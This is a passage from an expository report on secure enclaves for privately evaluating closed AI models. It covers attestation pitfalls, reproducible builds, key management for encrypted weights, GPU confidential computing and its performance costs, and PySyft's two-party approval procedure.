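In another faulty design, the report contains the nonce but not the hash of the session key, and the enclave sends its public key separately. An attacker on the network, perhaps the host, chooses the private number 3 and computes 5^3 mod 23 = 10. The attacker forwards the genuine report to the laptop but replaces the enclave's public key, 8, with 10.

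The laptop computes 10^15 mod 23 = 5, and the attacker computes 19^3 mod 23 = 5, so they share a key. The attacker also sends 10 to the enclave in place of the laptop's 19. The enclave computes 10^6 mod 23 = 6, and the attacker gets the same value from 8^3 mod 23. The attacker can decrypt the questions with the key derived from 5, copy them, re-encrypt them with the key derived from 6 and send them to the enclave. The test runs normally and the evaluator gets genuine results.

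The report was true, and a genuine chip was running the right software, but the evaluator had encrypted the file to somebody else. Putting H(A) in the report prevents this, because the laptop would hash 10 and find that the result didn't match H(A). The attacker can't change the report to match without the chip's attestation key.

Trail of Bits recommends going further and having the chip sign a value computed from the whole handshake, so that the report is valid for only one connection.

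### A matching hash of software nobody has read

The last of these failures can happen without any tampering with keys. Suppose the model owner builds the enclave's software and tells the evaluator what measurement to expect, and the chip reports that measurement. The match shows that the owner loaded the software it said it would. If that software writes every question to an outside log, the attestation confirms only that the leaking program is running. *The Provenance-Privacy Paradox* (2026), which examines Apple's enclave service, distinguishes attestation of a program's identity from attestation of its behaviour. Ordinary attestation covers only the program's identity.

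Nobody can recover a program from its hash, so the evaluator needs the source code, the human-readable version that programmers write. The evaluator also needs a way to check that the software with this hash came from that source code. Compiling the same source twice often produces slightly different files, because the tools insert the build time, a folder name or a list in arbitrary order. A reproducible build removes these differences, so anyone who compiles the source gets an identical file and therefore an identical measurement.

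The evaluator can then compile the published source, compute the measurement and compare it with the one in the chip's report. An evaluator without the skills to do this can rely on an auditor. Trask and colleagues note that a single honest person can expose a substituted program by publishing a mismatch.

*Confidential Inference Systems* (2025), by Anthropic and the AI security company Pattern Labs, treats the choice of who builds the software as a security problem. If the model owner builds it, the customer can't rule out an added function that reveals their data. If the cloud company builds it, the model owner has the same worry about the weights. A reproducible build solves this, but every step has to be reproducible: compiling the program, packing it into a container and turning the container into an enclave image.

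Where that isn't possible, the paper suggests using analysis tools to compare the finished program with its source, or adopting a program that a third party has already built and checked. Both give weaker assurance, because somebody has to interpret the differences a comparison tool finds, and trusting an already checked program means relying on whoever checked it.

Even with a perfectly reproducible build, the evaluator has to take a lot on trust. Somebody still has to read the source, and the Linux kernel alone has tens of millions of lines. In practice an evaluator would concentrate on the code written for the test and hope that other people have examined the rest. The build tools are another weak point. If everyone uses the same compromised compiler, everyone gets the same compromised program and the hashes match. Pattern Labs and Anthropic cite a 2016 security talk that showed enclave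 build tools being downloaded over an unencrypted connection, where an attacker could have replaced them. The chip's firmware is closed, so outsiders can't rebuild it. Owners may also refuse to show their inference code.

Trask and colleagues ran into these limits in the Gemini trial. Google's enclave operating system is open source, and Google publishes the expected measurements, but outsiders can't reproduce a build because each one takes a private signing key as an input. The trial also relied on Google's services to sign and verify the attestation report, which is a serious gap because the purpose was to hide the questions from Google. The paper lists both problems as work to be done.

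### Inputs that escape the measurement

Software can also be harmless when the chip measures it but become harmful because of something it loads later. The WhatsApp audit found two examples.

In the first, the system read a configuration file after the chip had taken the measurement. The file could set environment variables, which are settings that programs read when they start, including one that makes Linux load extra code into every program. A malicious insider at Meta could have used this variable to add code that recorded users' messages, and the attestation would still have looked correct. Meta now restricts which characters the settings may contain and checks for dangerous settings by name.

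The second involved the tables that tell an operating system what hardware it has. The host supplies these tables to a virtual machine, and the measurement didn't cover them. A malicious host could have described a fake device with permission to read and write protected memory, and the virtual machine would have granted it access, again with no change in the measurement. Meta fixed this with a new start-up program that verifies the tables, so tampering with them now changes the measurement.

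Trail of Bits also found that WhatsApp read the firmware version from the report, where old, compromised firmware could write a higher number. WhatsApp now reads it from AMD's certificate for the signing key, where it is much harder to fake.

Trail of Bits' *Meta WhatsApp Private Processing* (2025) lists 28 issues, eight of them high severity. Before launch, Meta fully resolved 16, partly resolved four, and chose to leave eight minor ones. Trail of Bits considers these implementation mistakes rather than flaws in the idea of an enclave, which seems right, but it expects other teams to make the same mistakes. Meta is a large company with experienced security engineers, so an evaluator whose enclave was built by a smaller team for a single test should probably expect more of these problems.

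### Where the encryption ends

A service provider can run a model in an enclave and still read everything its customers send. Pattern Labs and Anthropic distinguish two arrangements. In one, the customer's encrypted connection ends at the provider's servers, which decrypt the questions and forward them to the enclave. In the other, it ends inside the enclave, and the provider's servers only pass along data they can't read.

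| | Encryption ends at the provider | Encryption ends inside the enclave |
|---|---|---|
| Who can read the questions | The provider and the enclave | The enclave |
| What the customer's computer has to check | The provider's ordinary website certificate | The chip's attestation report |
| What the enclave can still protect | The model's weights | The weights and the questions |

The first arrangement makes sense for stopping a cloud company from stealing the weights, but it doesn't help an evaluator who wants to keep the questions from that provider. The two arrangements look the same to a casual user, because both use an encrypted connection and both let the service truthfully advertise that it uses enclaves. An evaluator should ask which machine holds the key that decrypts the questions.

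There are two ways to encrypt data so that it is decrypted inside the enclave. The customer can check the report and encrypt to the session key, as the laptop did above. Or the customer can encrypt the data using a key management service, which lets an enclave decrypt it only if the enclave presents an acceptable report. The second way leaves the customer's computer less to do, but whoever can change the service's rules can let a different program read the data.

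Anthropic's *Confidential Inference via Trusted Virtual Machines* (2025) sketches a design with two places where a user's text is readable. A request arrives encrypted at Anthropic's API server, which decrypts it, processes it and encrypts it again. The text stays encrypted until it reaches a small "loader" program, which decrypts it and sends it to the chips that run the model. Most of the software around the loader can change often without affecting security, because it never handles readable text.

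The post is mainly about the loader and doesn't cover the API server's security, which it calls equally important. For an evaluator, the API server would need the same sort of attestation as the loader, since it has access to the same questions. Anthropic also still relied on its cloud providers for physical security and for the hypervisor, the software that keeps virtual machines apart. It presented the work as early research and didn't promise a product.

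### What users of private AI clouds can check

Several companies now offer AI services, often called private AI clouds, that send users' data to enclaves. These services are designed to protect ordinary users, not evaluators, but the steps for checking an enclave and encrypting data to it are much the same. These services also show how much checking companies will allow in practice.

Apple's Private Cloud Compute, introduced in 2024, handles requests too demanding for a phone or laptop. Before the user's device sends the key that decrypts a request, it checks the server's attestation and looks for the server's software in a public log. Apple can add entries to this log but can't remove them. This makes it risky to write a special version for one victim, because the device will refuse any version that isn't in the log, and anyone can ask about a logged version. The log doesn't show that the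 software is safe.

Apple also publishes the software as finished programs and gives researchers a virtual environment in which to run them. *Unlocking Apple's Private Cloud Compute* (2026), an outside analysis, notes that even ordinary users can look up the state of the servers' software in logs on their devices. It also points out that Apple's promise to delete requests depends on the software, since no cryptographic protocol can force a server to erase what it has read. Deletion of an evaluator's questions would depend on the enclave's software in the same way.

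In June 2026 Apple extended the service to Google's data centres, using Intel processors and NVIDIA GPUs. Apple's *Expanding Private Cloud Compute* describes unusually strict measures. Apple counts all the software on the machine, including the host's operating system, as part of the trusted computing base, and keeps the same kind of add-only log of the hardware in use. For components that could leak user data, the attestation depends on at least two roots of trust from independent suppliers, so faking it would take more than one dishonest or careless manufacturer.

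*Powering the next era of Confidential AI* (Patil and Lagar-Cavilla, 2026) also reports that Google and Apple built an open-source version of the host's software so that outsiders can inspect it. Apple said it would phase in the full set of protections during a summer preview, and InfoQ (2026) reported that an updated security guide would follow later in the year.

Meta records the hashes of WhatsApp's enclave software in a log that Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, maintains. The client refuses to connect to software whose hash isn't in the log. According to Meta, the log is a simple list, not the tree of hashes that lets outsiders detect a deleted entry in many transparency logs. Approved researchers can get the programs themselves, sometimes after a delay of up to about 90 days for unpublished security fixes. The models and their standing instructions stay private, but their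 hashes go in the log. An evaluator could use the same method to confirm, without seeing a model's weights, that two tests ran on the same model. Meta has made progress towards reproducible builds, but Trail of Bits reports that full reproducibility remains difficult.

With both services, the company being checked supplies the software that does the checking. An iPhone checks Apple's servers, and WhatsApp checks Meta's. That's reasonable for a consumer product, but an evaluator should use software from somebody else.

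These services also protect users by keeping each one anonymous among many others. An outside relay conceals the user's network address, and the system picks an enclave without identifying the user, so an attacker who controls one enclave can't steer a chosen person to it. A scheduled evaluation on its own enclave lacks this protection because the model owner knows whose questions are coming and when. The evaluator therefore depends more on the attestation.

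Google's Private AI Compute, which runs Gemini models on Google's own chips, offered users less to check when it launched in November 2025. Google said an outside auditor had validated the design, and Google planned further attestation so others could verify more themselves. The Hacker News (2025) reported that the auditor, NCC Group, found three problems in the attestation code. NCC Group also found that the timing of traffic through the relay could reveal a user's identity under certain conditions. Google rated that risk as low because so many people use the system at once.

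OpenAI began testing Private Inference with a small group of business customers in November 2026. *OpenAI Starts Testing Private Inference* (Faisal, 2026) reported that prompts and answers stay encrypted except inside attested hardware, and that OpenAI says outsiders can verify the hardware's security. But ITHome's *迈出“全民隐私智能”第一步* reported that OpenAI hadn't disclosed how the system works, so outsiders have little to examine for now.

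Most business customers still can't get this kind of protection from the services they normally use to rent models. *Beyond Training* (2026), a survey of ways to regulate AI models in use, found that two large services, Google's Vertex AI and Amazon's Bedrock, didn't offer enclave-protected inference through their APIs, even though both companies sell enclaves separately. It judged that providers could add this protection within two or three years if a regulator required it.

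Confer, an AI assistant from Moxie Marlinspike, creator of the encrypted messenger Signal, goes furthest in letting users check its claims. According to an Ars Technica article republished by SoylentNews, the service runs entirely on open-source software, including its language models, and lets users verify cryptographically that this software is in place. Confer can publish all of this software because it has no secret model to protect.

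## How model weights reach the enclave and its GPU

Unlike Confer, which publishes everything, a company that wants to keep its model secret has to get the weights into the enclave, and from there to the GPUs, without giving the host a readable copy. The owner can encrypt the weights once and control who gets the key. Encrypting them to the enclave's session key, as an evaluator does with test questions, would mean encrypting hundreds of gigabytes again every time an enclave started.

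### Two keys and a rule for releasing them

Suppose a model has 400 billion weights, stored at one byte each, so the file is 400 gigabytes. The owner generates a random 32-byte data key, D, and encrypts the weights with it. The owner then encrypts D with a second key, K, which is known as wrapping:

C = Enc(D, weights)

W = Enc(K, D)

C is still about 400 gigabytes, and W is under 100 bytes. The owner can keep both in ordinary cloud storage because neither is useful without K. K stays in a key management service, which uses the keys it holds but doesn't release them.

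Pattern Labs and Anthropic describe how the enclave then gets the data key:

1. The enclave copies C and W from storage.
2. It gets an attestation report that vouches for its session key.
3. It sends the report and W to the key management service over an encrypted connection. The host's software carries this traffic but can't read it.
4. The service checks the report against its policy, which lists the measurements of approved software. If the report passes, the service unwraps W and encrypts D to the enclave's public key.
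5. The enclave decrypts D and uses it to decrypt the weights in protected memory.

With two keys, the service handles only a few dozen bytes and never has access to the weights. To replace K, the owner rewraps 32 bytes instead of re-encrypting 400 gigabytes. The owner can also approve new software by adding a measurement to the policy.

The encrypted file also contains the model's architecture. The program in the enclave normally isn't secret, and anyone who gets a copy can reverse engineer it. Pattern Labs and Anthropic therefore recommend a generic program that can load many models and contains none of the owner's secrets. Such a program should also need few changes, so the owner has fewer new versions to check.

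The key also has to reach the right program inside the enclave. Many cloud companies manage their customers' software with Kubernetes, which lets an administrator open a command line inside a confidential virtual machine. *ENCLAVEX* (Schambach, Arnautov and colleagues, 2026) addresses this by attesting the application separately from the virtual machine around it. Its key service releases secrets only to the attested application, and the operating system blocks the functions an administrator could use to copy the application's memory.

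### Where the key service sits

Under this arrangement, a thief can steal the weights without learning a key, by changing the policy or fooling the service that applies it. Pattern Labs and Anthropic compare three places where the owner could put that service.

The most convenient place to keep the decryption key is the owner's account with the cloud company that hosts the enclave, since some cloud key services can already check attestation reports. But a thief who takes over the owner's administrator account could find the encrypted weights and their key, edit the key's policy to allow decryption from the thief's own account, and decrypt the weights without touching the enclave. Somebody who had compromised the cloud company could do the same.

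If the owner runs the service on its own machine, the policy is out of the cloud company's reach. But the owner then has to protect that machine and its connection to the enclave, and write the code that checks attestation reports. This code is easy to get wrong, as the WhatsApp audit showed.

The service can also run inside the enclave, which generates the wrapping key and never releases it. This removes the outside connection, but the key may be lost when the enclave shuts down, because some virtual-machine enclaves have neither permanent storage nor a way to regenerate the same secret after a restart. One workaround is to keep an enclave running all the time with the key in its encrypted memory, but a power failure would destroy the key.

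| Location of the key service | How a thief could get the weights | Main practical difficulty |
|---|---|---|
| The owner's cloud account | Take over the account, or compromise the cloud company, and edit the policy | Protecting the administrator accounts |
| The owner's own machine | Break into the machine, or get a false attestation report past its checks | Building and running a secure key service |
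| Inside the enclave | Break the enclave or exploit a flaw in its software | Keeping the key through a restart |

For an occasional evaluation, running the service on the owner's own machine seems the best compromise, because the owner can leave the service disconnected most of the time. Pattern Labs and Anthropic suggest this for particularly risky models. The owner would connect the service when the enclave needed the weights, log the release and disconnect it again, so a thief would have little time to try a false report.

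None of these arrangements protects unencrypted copies of the weights stored elsewhere. Training normally produces one, and the owner may also have backups. Pattern Labs and Anthropic suggest destroying the unencrypted copies after encryption, or training the model inside an enclave so that even the owner never has one. Either would be a large change for a company whose researchers work with the weights every day.

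### What the highest security levels require

For models whose theft would be most dangerous, RAND (2024) likewise recommends keeping the key inside the enclave. The American research organisation interviewed about 30 experts for *Securing AI Model Weights*, which defines five security levels by the attackers each could stop. Security Level 4 (SL4) is meant to stop most standard operations by leading state-sponsored hacking groups. SL5 is meant to stop the few operations that the most capable states give top priority.

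SL4 calls for enclaves when they are available, on three conditions:

- The enclave protects against physical attacks.
- The key that encrypts the weights is generated inside the enclave and stored nowhere else.
- The enclave runs only signed code that somebody has specified and audited in advance, and this code outputs nothing but the model's response.

GPU enclaves did not meet the physical condition in mid-2024, and RAND considered the technology too immature for production use. RAND's experts overwhelmingly agreed that enclaves were an important next step, though they disagreed about much of what SL4 and SL5 should contain.

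The condition on outputs would let an outside evaluator ask questions and read the answers, but not record the model's internal activity, which is one of the main reasons to want white-box access. An owner who followed SL4 literally would have to make an exception to allow such recording.

RAND's SL4 also requires four independent layers of security, each of which should hold if all the others fail. One measure is a hardware limit on how much data can leave the protected machines, for example 5% of the weights' size per year. At that rate, a thief who broke into the enclave would need 20 years to copy the whole 400-gigabyte file, although RAND warns that a partial or compressed copy could also be dangerous.

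SL5 calls for eight independent security layers and a completely isolated network for weights that aren't in production use. RAND judged in 2024 that nobody could yet achieve it. A task force of engineers and security specialists, including people from the leading AI companies, is now trying to make it possible by 2028 or 2029. The group's first draft, *SL5 Standard for AI Security* (Thiergart, Tzfati and colleagues, 2026), assumes an attacker with the equivalent of 1,000 skilled people, years to work and up to $1 billion to spend.

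The draft calls for an AI chip that protects itself. Data should arrive encrypted from its source and become readable only inside the chip. The chip should be able to deny the host access regardless of what software the host runs, encrypt its traffic with other chips, and resist tampering. NVIDIA's Blackwell GPUs, the generation after Hopper, fall short because they depend on the processor's enclave to isolate memory and verify code. Chipmakers also exclude physical attacks from their security guarantees. Thiergart and colleagues add that current chips can't prevent an attacker from combining several permitted operations to extract data.

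The draft's rules on incoming data require the company to screen everything a model might read, including evaluation data and prompts, for content designed to attack the model. People then review what the software flags. An evaluator with secret questions could hardly accept this unless the screening took place inside the enclave and nobody at the company could read the flagged questions.

RAND's *Highly Secure Inference Data Centers* gives a more optimistic assessment of SL5. It proposes data centres that only run finished models, with links that can physically carry data in only one direction, and concludes that proven technology is enough to build them today. But these centres would have limited connections, fixed software and restricted physical access. RAND acknowledges that these constraints limit their general use, and recommends them for national security, emergency response and pilot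 projects.

### A closed model in somebody else's building

Physical protection matters most when the owner doesn't control the building. Pattern Labs and Anthropic list deployment on a customer's own servers as one use of enclaves. The owner could deliver C and W to the customer, keep K on its own machine, and release the data key whenever an approved enclave started. The owner could later stop releasing the key, but an enclave already running could keep using the weights until it shut down. A site with no outside connection would need another way to get the key.

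A government evaluator could use the same arrangement to run a closed model on its own premises. The evaluator's secret questions would never leave the building, even in encrypted form, so it wouldn't have to trust a cloud company. The model owner would bear the risk instead, because its weights would be on a machine that the evaluator could take apart.

NVIDIA's protection is designed to withstand a host who controls the server's software and watches the link between the processor and the GPU. According to Gu and colleagues, it doesn't cover sophisticated physical attacks, such as opening the chip's package to probe the memory inside. They think such an attack would be difficult and would probably destroy the chip. A model's owner might accept that risk with an ordinary commercial model and a customer it knows. The protection would not meet RAND's conditions for a model that needs SL4.

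### From the processor to the GPU

A GPU is a separate chip with its own memory, but a confidential virtual machine protects only the processor and the memory that the processor encrypts. On an ordinary server, the host's administrators can read and change the GPU's settings and memory, and someone with the right equipment can record the data sent over PCIe, the link between the processor and the GPU. If only the processor had an enclave, the weights would be exposed as soon as the program sent them to the GPU.

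The GPU can calculate only with readable weights, so NVIDIA protects the GPU's memory mainly by blocking access to it. Most of the memory becomes a protected region that the host can't read. Once a program is using this region, the GPU's calculating units can't use unprotected memory.

Gu and colleagues pieced together how an H100 sets up this protection:

1. Security processors on the GPU check NVIDIA's signature on each piece of firmware before running it.
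2. NVIDIA's driver and the GPU derive 44 keys from the secret they have agreed on, so that different kinds of traffic have different keys.
3. The GPU closes most of the openings through which the host normally controls it.
4. The virtual machine verifies the GPU's attestation report and allows the GPU to start work.

To test the barrier, Gu and colleagues tried to read about 4.2 million locations in the GPU's control registers. Without protection, 7.94% returned a value other than zero or an error. With protection on, 1,042 locations (0.02%) did. NVIDIA hasn't documented what all these locations do, so outsiders can't tell whether any of them reveal something useful.

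The model owner needs evidence about both the processor and the GPU before releasing the data key. If the key service checks only the processor's report, the owner has to rely on the approved software to reject a fake or unprotected GPU. The design by Schambach and colleagues avoids this by sending reports from both the virtual machine and the GPU to the key service.

The weights can then cross the link. A program in the virtual machine decrypts them with the data key. NVIDIA's software encrypts them again with a key it shares with the GPU and puts the result in a staging buffer, an area of ordinary memory that both the virtual machine and the GPU can reach. The GPU copies the data from there, checks that nobody has altered it, and decrypts it into the protected region. The GPU uses a different key to encrypt data it sends back to the processor. A counter changes with every message, so the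 host can't replay old messages.

The host can still learn something from this traffic. Gu and colleagues found that NVIDIA encrypts the contents of management commands but leaves much of their metadata readable. An attacker could change this metadata to repeat, drop or reorder commands. The time some transfers take also reveals their approximate size. These leaks don't reveal the weights, but the researchers couldn't fully examine the route that weights normally take because NVIDIA keeps that part of its software closed.

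In *Benchmarking Confidential Computing Performance on NVIDIA Blackwell GPUs*, Asad and Grunseid (2026) copied 8.25 gibibytes from a GPU to the processor and recorded 17,505 decryption operations covering 8.44 gibibytes. This suggests that the software encrypts essentially everything in such a transfer. Asad and Grunseid were studying speed, though, and didn't try to attack the system.

Processor and GPU makers are working on a more direct connection, called trusted I/O. The GPU would join the virtual machine's protected area and read the machine's memory directly over a hardware-encrypted link, so software would no longer have to encrypt data and copy it through a staging buffer. Linux gained initial support for this in February 2026, but NVIDIA's Hopper and Blackwell GPUs still used staging buffers at the time. Asad and Grunseid reported in June that the necessary hardware and driver support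 wasn't yet shipping for their system.

### GPUs without their own protection

Some AI chips have no enclave features, and a host may choose not to use those features on chips that do. Pattern Labs and Anthropic describe how to attach such a chip to the processor's enclave. The hardware or the hypervisor can allow only the enclave to use the GPU, perhaps with areas of memory that one side can write to and only the other can read. Alternatively, the designers can treat the whole virtual machine, including its attached GPU, as the protected area.

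This keeps other programs on the server away from the weights. But the weights cross the link unencrypted, so somebody with access to the hardware could record them, and Pattern Labs and Anthropic warn that the method isn't fully secure. The GPU also can't prove its identity or what firmware it runs. The method might protect the weights well enough for an owner who hosts the enclave in its own data centre. It is a poor choice for an evaluator trying to hide questions from that owner, because the owner would control both the hypervisor and the building.

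### When a model needs several GPUs

The strongest models don't fit on one GPU, so their weights are spread over several. These GPUs exchange partial results many times for each piece of text they produce. NVIDIA's servers carry this traffic over NVLink, a fast connection between GPUs, and anyone who could read it would see some of the model's internal activity and learn something about the questions.

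NVIDIA added protection for traffic between GPUs in stages. The first software for Hopper allowed only one protected GPU per virtual machine. A later mode, Protected PCIe, allowed several, but it encrypted only the links to the processor and left NVLink unencrypted for speed. Blackwell can encrypt NVLink as well. So an owner or evaluator who is told that a multi-GPU Hopper server runs in "confidential mode" should ask whether the traffic between its GPUs is encrypted.

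Asad and Grunseid used a Blackwell server with eight B200 GPUs, each with about 183 gigabytes of usable memory. Together the GPUs have nearly 1.5 terabytes, enough for a model with a trillion weights at one byte each but not at two. Larger models have to run on several servers. GPUs in different servers normally send data to each other directly through the network cards, but Blackwell's confidential mode blocks this. The data has to go from the first GPU to its processor, across the network to the other processor, and from there to the second GPU, with encryption at both ends. Asad and Grunseid didn't measure how much this reduces performance, so we can't tell from their results how well enclaves would work for a model spread over a rack of servers.

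### What the protection costs

Published measurements of the slowdown range from zero to more than 60%. The main ones compare how many tokens (fragments of words) a system produces per second with and without protection.

Some of the early reassuring figures come from *Confidential Computing on NVIDIA Hopper GPUs* (Zhu, Yin and colleagues, 2024). With one request at a time, protection slowed Llama-3.1-8B, a small open model, by 6.9% on an H100 and 8.8% on an H200. A model with 70 billion weights showed no measurable slowdown on the H100, but it was producing only about 2.5 tokens per second, so a few extra milliseconds of work per token would hardly show.

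Schambach and colleagues also ran Llama-3.1-8B on an H200, with an Intel confidential virtual machine. They measured a throughput overhead of 62.8% when the GPU handled one request at a time and 35.0% when it handled 64. Their software was highly optimised, with weights compressed to eight bits, so a fixed delay would take up a larger share of each step. Their unprotected run also had no enclave on the processor, whereas Zhu and colleagues describe switching protection on and off only on the GPU. These differences probably explain much of the gap between the two papers' results.

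| Measured by | Hardware and model | Workload | Throughput cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Zhu and colleagues | One H200, Llama-3.1-8B | One request at a time | 8.8% |
| Zhu and colleagues | One H100, Llama-3.1-70B | One request at a time | About 0% |
| Schambach and colleagues | One H200, Llama-3.1-8B | One request at a time | 62.8% |
| Schambach and colleagues | One H200, Llama-3.1-8B | 64 requests at once | 35.0% |
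| Asad and Grunseid | One B200, Qwen3-8B, standard software | 16 to 64 requests at once | 34–39% |
| Asad and Grunseid | One B200, Qwen2.5-72B, modified software | 1 to 32 requests at once | Under 1% |
| Asad and Grunseid | Eight B200s, MiniMax-M2.7 | 32 requests at once, 2,048-token answers | About 3% |
| Asad and Grunseid | Eight B200s, MiniMax-M2.7 | 32 requests at once, 256-token answers | 14.4% |

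Asad and Grunseid, of the company Confidential.ai, did the most to explain the delay. They used the same server, disks and GPUs for each pair of runs and changed only the protection. Nearly all the delay came from communication, while the calculations on the GPU took almost exactly as long either way. Protection didn't increase power use, and it reserved only 700 megabytes of each GPU's memory.

One part of it comes from commands. The processor tells the GPU which operation to do next, and each such command took 3.5 microseconds without protection and 15.7 with it. Asad and Grunseid ran Qwen3.5-9B with eight requests at once, which took about 185 commands to produce the next token for every request:

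extra time per step ≈ 185 × 12 µs ≈ 2.2 ms

Protection added a measured 2.28 milliseconds to a step that took 4.51 milliseconds without it, making each step about 50% longer. The same delay would make a 45-millisecond step only 5% longer. Larger models and larger batches of requests tend to show smaller percentage slowdowns because their steps take longer.

Software can remove most of this delay by recording a sequence of commands once and sending it to the GPU as a single command. In a synthetic test with 181 operations per step, protection made the step 2.41 times as long when the processor sent the commands individually, but only 1.04 times as long when it sent them together.

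Protection also slows the GPU by making it wait. A well-designed system copies each new token back to the processor while the GPU works on the next one. With protection on, the standard version of SGLang, a popular program for running language models, had to finish each copy first, leaving the GPU idle. This is the main cause of the 34–39% slowdown with Qwen3-8B. Asad and Grunseid report that moving the copying to a separate thread cut the time per token on a single GPU from 8.68 to 5.63 milliseconds, the same as without protection. Their slowdown figure of under 1% comes from a much larger model, which would have slowed less even without the change.

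With several GPUs, encrypting NVLink causes a slowdown that better software can't remove. It reduced the speed of bulk transfers between GPUs by 11–18% and made short messages take about four times as long. The effect on a whole model depends on how much data the GPUs exchange. MiniMax-M2.7, with 229 billion weights, ran about 3% slower on eight GPUs but only 1.5% slower on four, because fewer GPUs took part in each exchange. The four GPUs still produced 94% as many tokens as the eight. Training involves much more traffic between GPUs, and protection made it about 10–13% slower in the main tests.

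Encryption also makes loading the weights slower. Encrypted transfers to one GPU ran at about 10 gigabytes per second in one of Asad and Grunseid's tests and 3.5 in another, compared with 51.6 without encryption. Split across eight GPUs in parallel, the 400-gigabyte model in the example would take 5 to 14 seconds to transfer instead of one. The transfer and attestation each happen once per start-up. Schambach and colleagues measured attestation at about 1.2 seconds with the checking service on the same machine.

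A claim that enclaves slow models by "under 5%" can therefore be true of one system and badly wrong about another with the same GPU, so it means little without the model, the software, the number of GPUs, the number of simultaneous requests and the length of the answers. Answer length matters a lot for evaluations. A model has to process the whole question before it answers, and on several GPUs this involves a large burst of encrypted traffic. A long answer spreads the delay from that burst over many tokens. With MiniMax-M2.7, the slowdown fell from 14.4% for answers of 256 tokens to about 1% for answers of 2,048 tokens in the same series of tests, although repeated runs put the slowdown for the longer answers nearer 3%.

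A multiple-choice test, with long questions and one-letter answers, is therefore close to the worst case, while a test in which the model writes long solutions is close to the best. Engineers may also struggle to find out why a test is slow, because confidential mode disables the usual GPU timing tools, which could leak information. A 14% loss in speed makes an evaluator's one-hour test take about 70 minutes, whereas a company serving millions of users would have to buy many more GPUs to make up for it.

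## How two parties approve code that each wants to hide

Once the weights and the test questions are in the same enclave, each party's code can access the other's secrets. The model owner's inference code has to read the questions to answer them, and the evaluator's grading code runs on the machine that holds the weights. The chip's encryption keeps the host out, but it doesn't stop either program from copying what it reads and sending it to the party that wrote the program.

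Trask and colleagues name two guarantees that an enclave provides against its host, privacy and veracity. Privacy means the host can't see a customer's data, and veracity means the host can't pass off the result of some other program or data as genuine. Both guarantees can hold while the software passes one customer's data to the other customer.

### When both sides can read the program

The simplest case with two parties is the millionaires' problem, which the computer scientist Andrew Yao posed in 1982. Two millionaires want to know which of them is richer without revealing their bank balances. With an enclave, one of them can launch a short open-source program that accepts a number from each, outputs the name of the person with the larger number, deletes everything and shuts down. Both read the program, check that the chip's signed measurement matches it, and send their encrypted balances.

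Suppose Ana has $3.2 million and Ben has $2.7 million. The program outputs "Ana", and Ben learns only that Ana has more than he does. Either of them can launch the enclave, because a different program would have a different measurement.

The shutdown matters as much as the comparison. If Ben's balance stayed in the enclave and Ana could rerun the program with any number she liked, she could halve the range of possible balances each time and find any balance under $16 million to the nearest dollar in 24 runs. Ana and Ben therefore have to agree on how often the program may run as well as on what it does.

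The same method works for testing an AI model if both sides can read all the code. In the 2024 pilot they could, because the model was GPT-2, which is old and public, and the evaluator's researcher could see its whole architecture. But the inference code for a secret model reveals its architecture. The evaluator's grading code may also contain secrets, such as a list of the details that make an answer dangerous. Each party would then have to approve code it can't fully read.

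### The PySyft procedure

Both pilots used PySyft, OpenMined's open-source software for running code on data that the code's author isn't allowed to see. One party launches and pays for the enclave, which has PySyft inside it. In return, that party gets only the ability to turn the enclave off. It can't read the other party's data or approve a computation alone. If the model's owner launched the enclave, it could stop a test that seemed to be going badly. The evaluator would know that the test was interrupted but would have no score, so it has good reason to insist that the owner doesn't see the results first.

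Both parties check the attestation report. The evaluator then has to write code for a model it can't see, so the owner supplies a mock, a fake model that accepts the same inputs as the real one and returns outputs in the same format. The evaluator supplies mock questions for the same reason. A mock model might answer everything with random words, which is enough to show whether the grading code runs. In an example from OpenMined's *Syft Code Policies*, the real data is the list 1, 2, 3 and the mock is 4, 5, 6. Anyone who runs code without permission gets the result for 4, 5, 6, with a notice that it comes from mock data. The parties can skip the mocks if the model has a standard interface the evaluator already knows.

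The evaluator submits the finished code with policies, which are rules that PySyft enforces when the code runs. An input policy ties the code to one specific dataset or model, so nobody can reuse the approval on another. An output policy can limit the code to a single run, which would have stopped Ana. The version of PySyft in the guide came with only a few policies. Users who wanted a different one, such as a policy that released only averages, had to write it themselves or rely on people reading the code.

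*Part 4* of OpenMined's medical research tutorial shows what a reviewer does. Rachel, a researcher, wants to train a model on a cancer centre's records. Owen, who is responsible for the records, reads her code, which returns only two accuracy scores. He runs it on the mock data and gets the same scores as Rachel, about 0.67 and 0.59. He then runs it on the real data and approves the request. Both times, PySyft warns him that the code could be unsafe. In another guide, OpenMined tells reviewers to look for print statements and code that exports raw rows of data, and to check which software packages the code uses.

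Owen has an advantage because he controls all the data and can look at the real result before anyone else does. In a double-blind evaluation, the model owner can't try the evaluator's code on the real questions, so it has to decide whether to approve it from the code and the mock result.

PySyft runs the code only after both parties have approved it. In the 2024 pilot, according to *Enabling External Scrutiny of AI Systems with Privacy-Enhancing Technologies* (2025), each party could approve or deny every computation in the evaluation. *Designing for Secure Enclave Collaboration*, a case study by a designer who worked on OpenMined's approval process, reports that organisations had more trouble with these decisions than with the computing. They found it hard to interpret low-level security guarantees and were unsure how the system would enforce a policy. One prototype let people see a project's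 purpose and conditions, discuss it in a chat, and vote on each computation that affected their data.

The two pilots kept private material in different places before approval. In 2024, Trask and colleagues kept each party's data on its own server and sent it to the enclave only after both parties had approved. In the procedure for the Gemini trial, the parties upload their code and data first, and PySyft holds them in the enclave until both parties approve. The 2024 procedure seems safer for a party that might refuse. The Gemini procedure lets the enclave check hidden code before anyone approves it, but that check doesn't require the weights or questions to be in the enclave yet.

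After approval, the enclave runs the code and releases the result to one or both parties, as they specified. In the 2024 pilot, only the researcher who started the evaluation got the result. The enclave then deleted what was left and shut down.

The chip doesn't enforce these steps directly. Its measurement covers PySyft and the layers underneath, but the parties upload their own code after start-up, so they depend on PySyft to run only the approved code. GitLab's *CVE-2026-31220* (2026), an entry in a database of software flaws, reports that PySyft versions up to 0.9.5 didn't check submitted code for dangerous operations, such as opening files or running commands. These versions also ran approved code inside the server's own process without proper isolation, so one dangerous line that a reviewer missed could have given the submitter control of the whole server.

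The Gemini trial used version 0.10, which the entry doesn't list as affected. *A Confidential Computing Transparency Framework for a Comprehensive Trust Chain* (2024) points out that attestation can't guarantee the absence of vulnerabilities or back doors, so it would have accepted the flawed versions too. A safer design would put each party's code in a separate sandbox inside the enclave, with a small monitor that intercepts every attempt to escape.

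### Redaction with an allowlist

Trask and colleagues propose a compromise for code that has to stay secret. Any program can be broken into smaller and smaller functions, until the pieces no longer contain anything worth hiding. For example, the way a company arranges a model's layers may be secret, but the additions and multiplications inside those layers are standard operations in PyTorch and JAX, two open-source libraries for building AI models.

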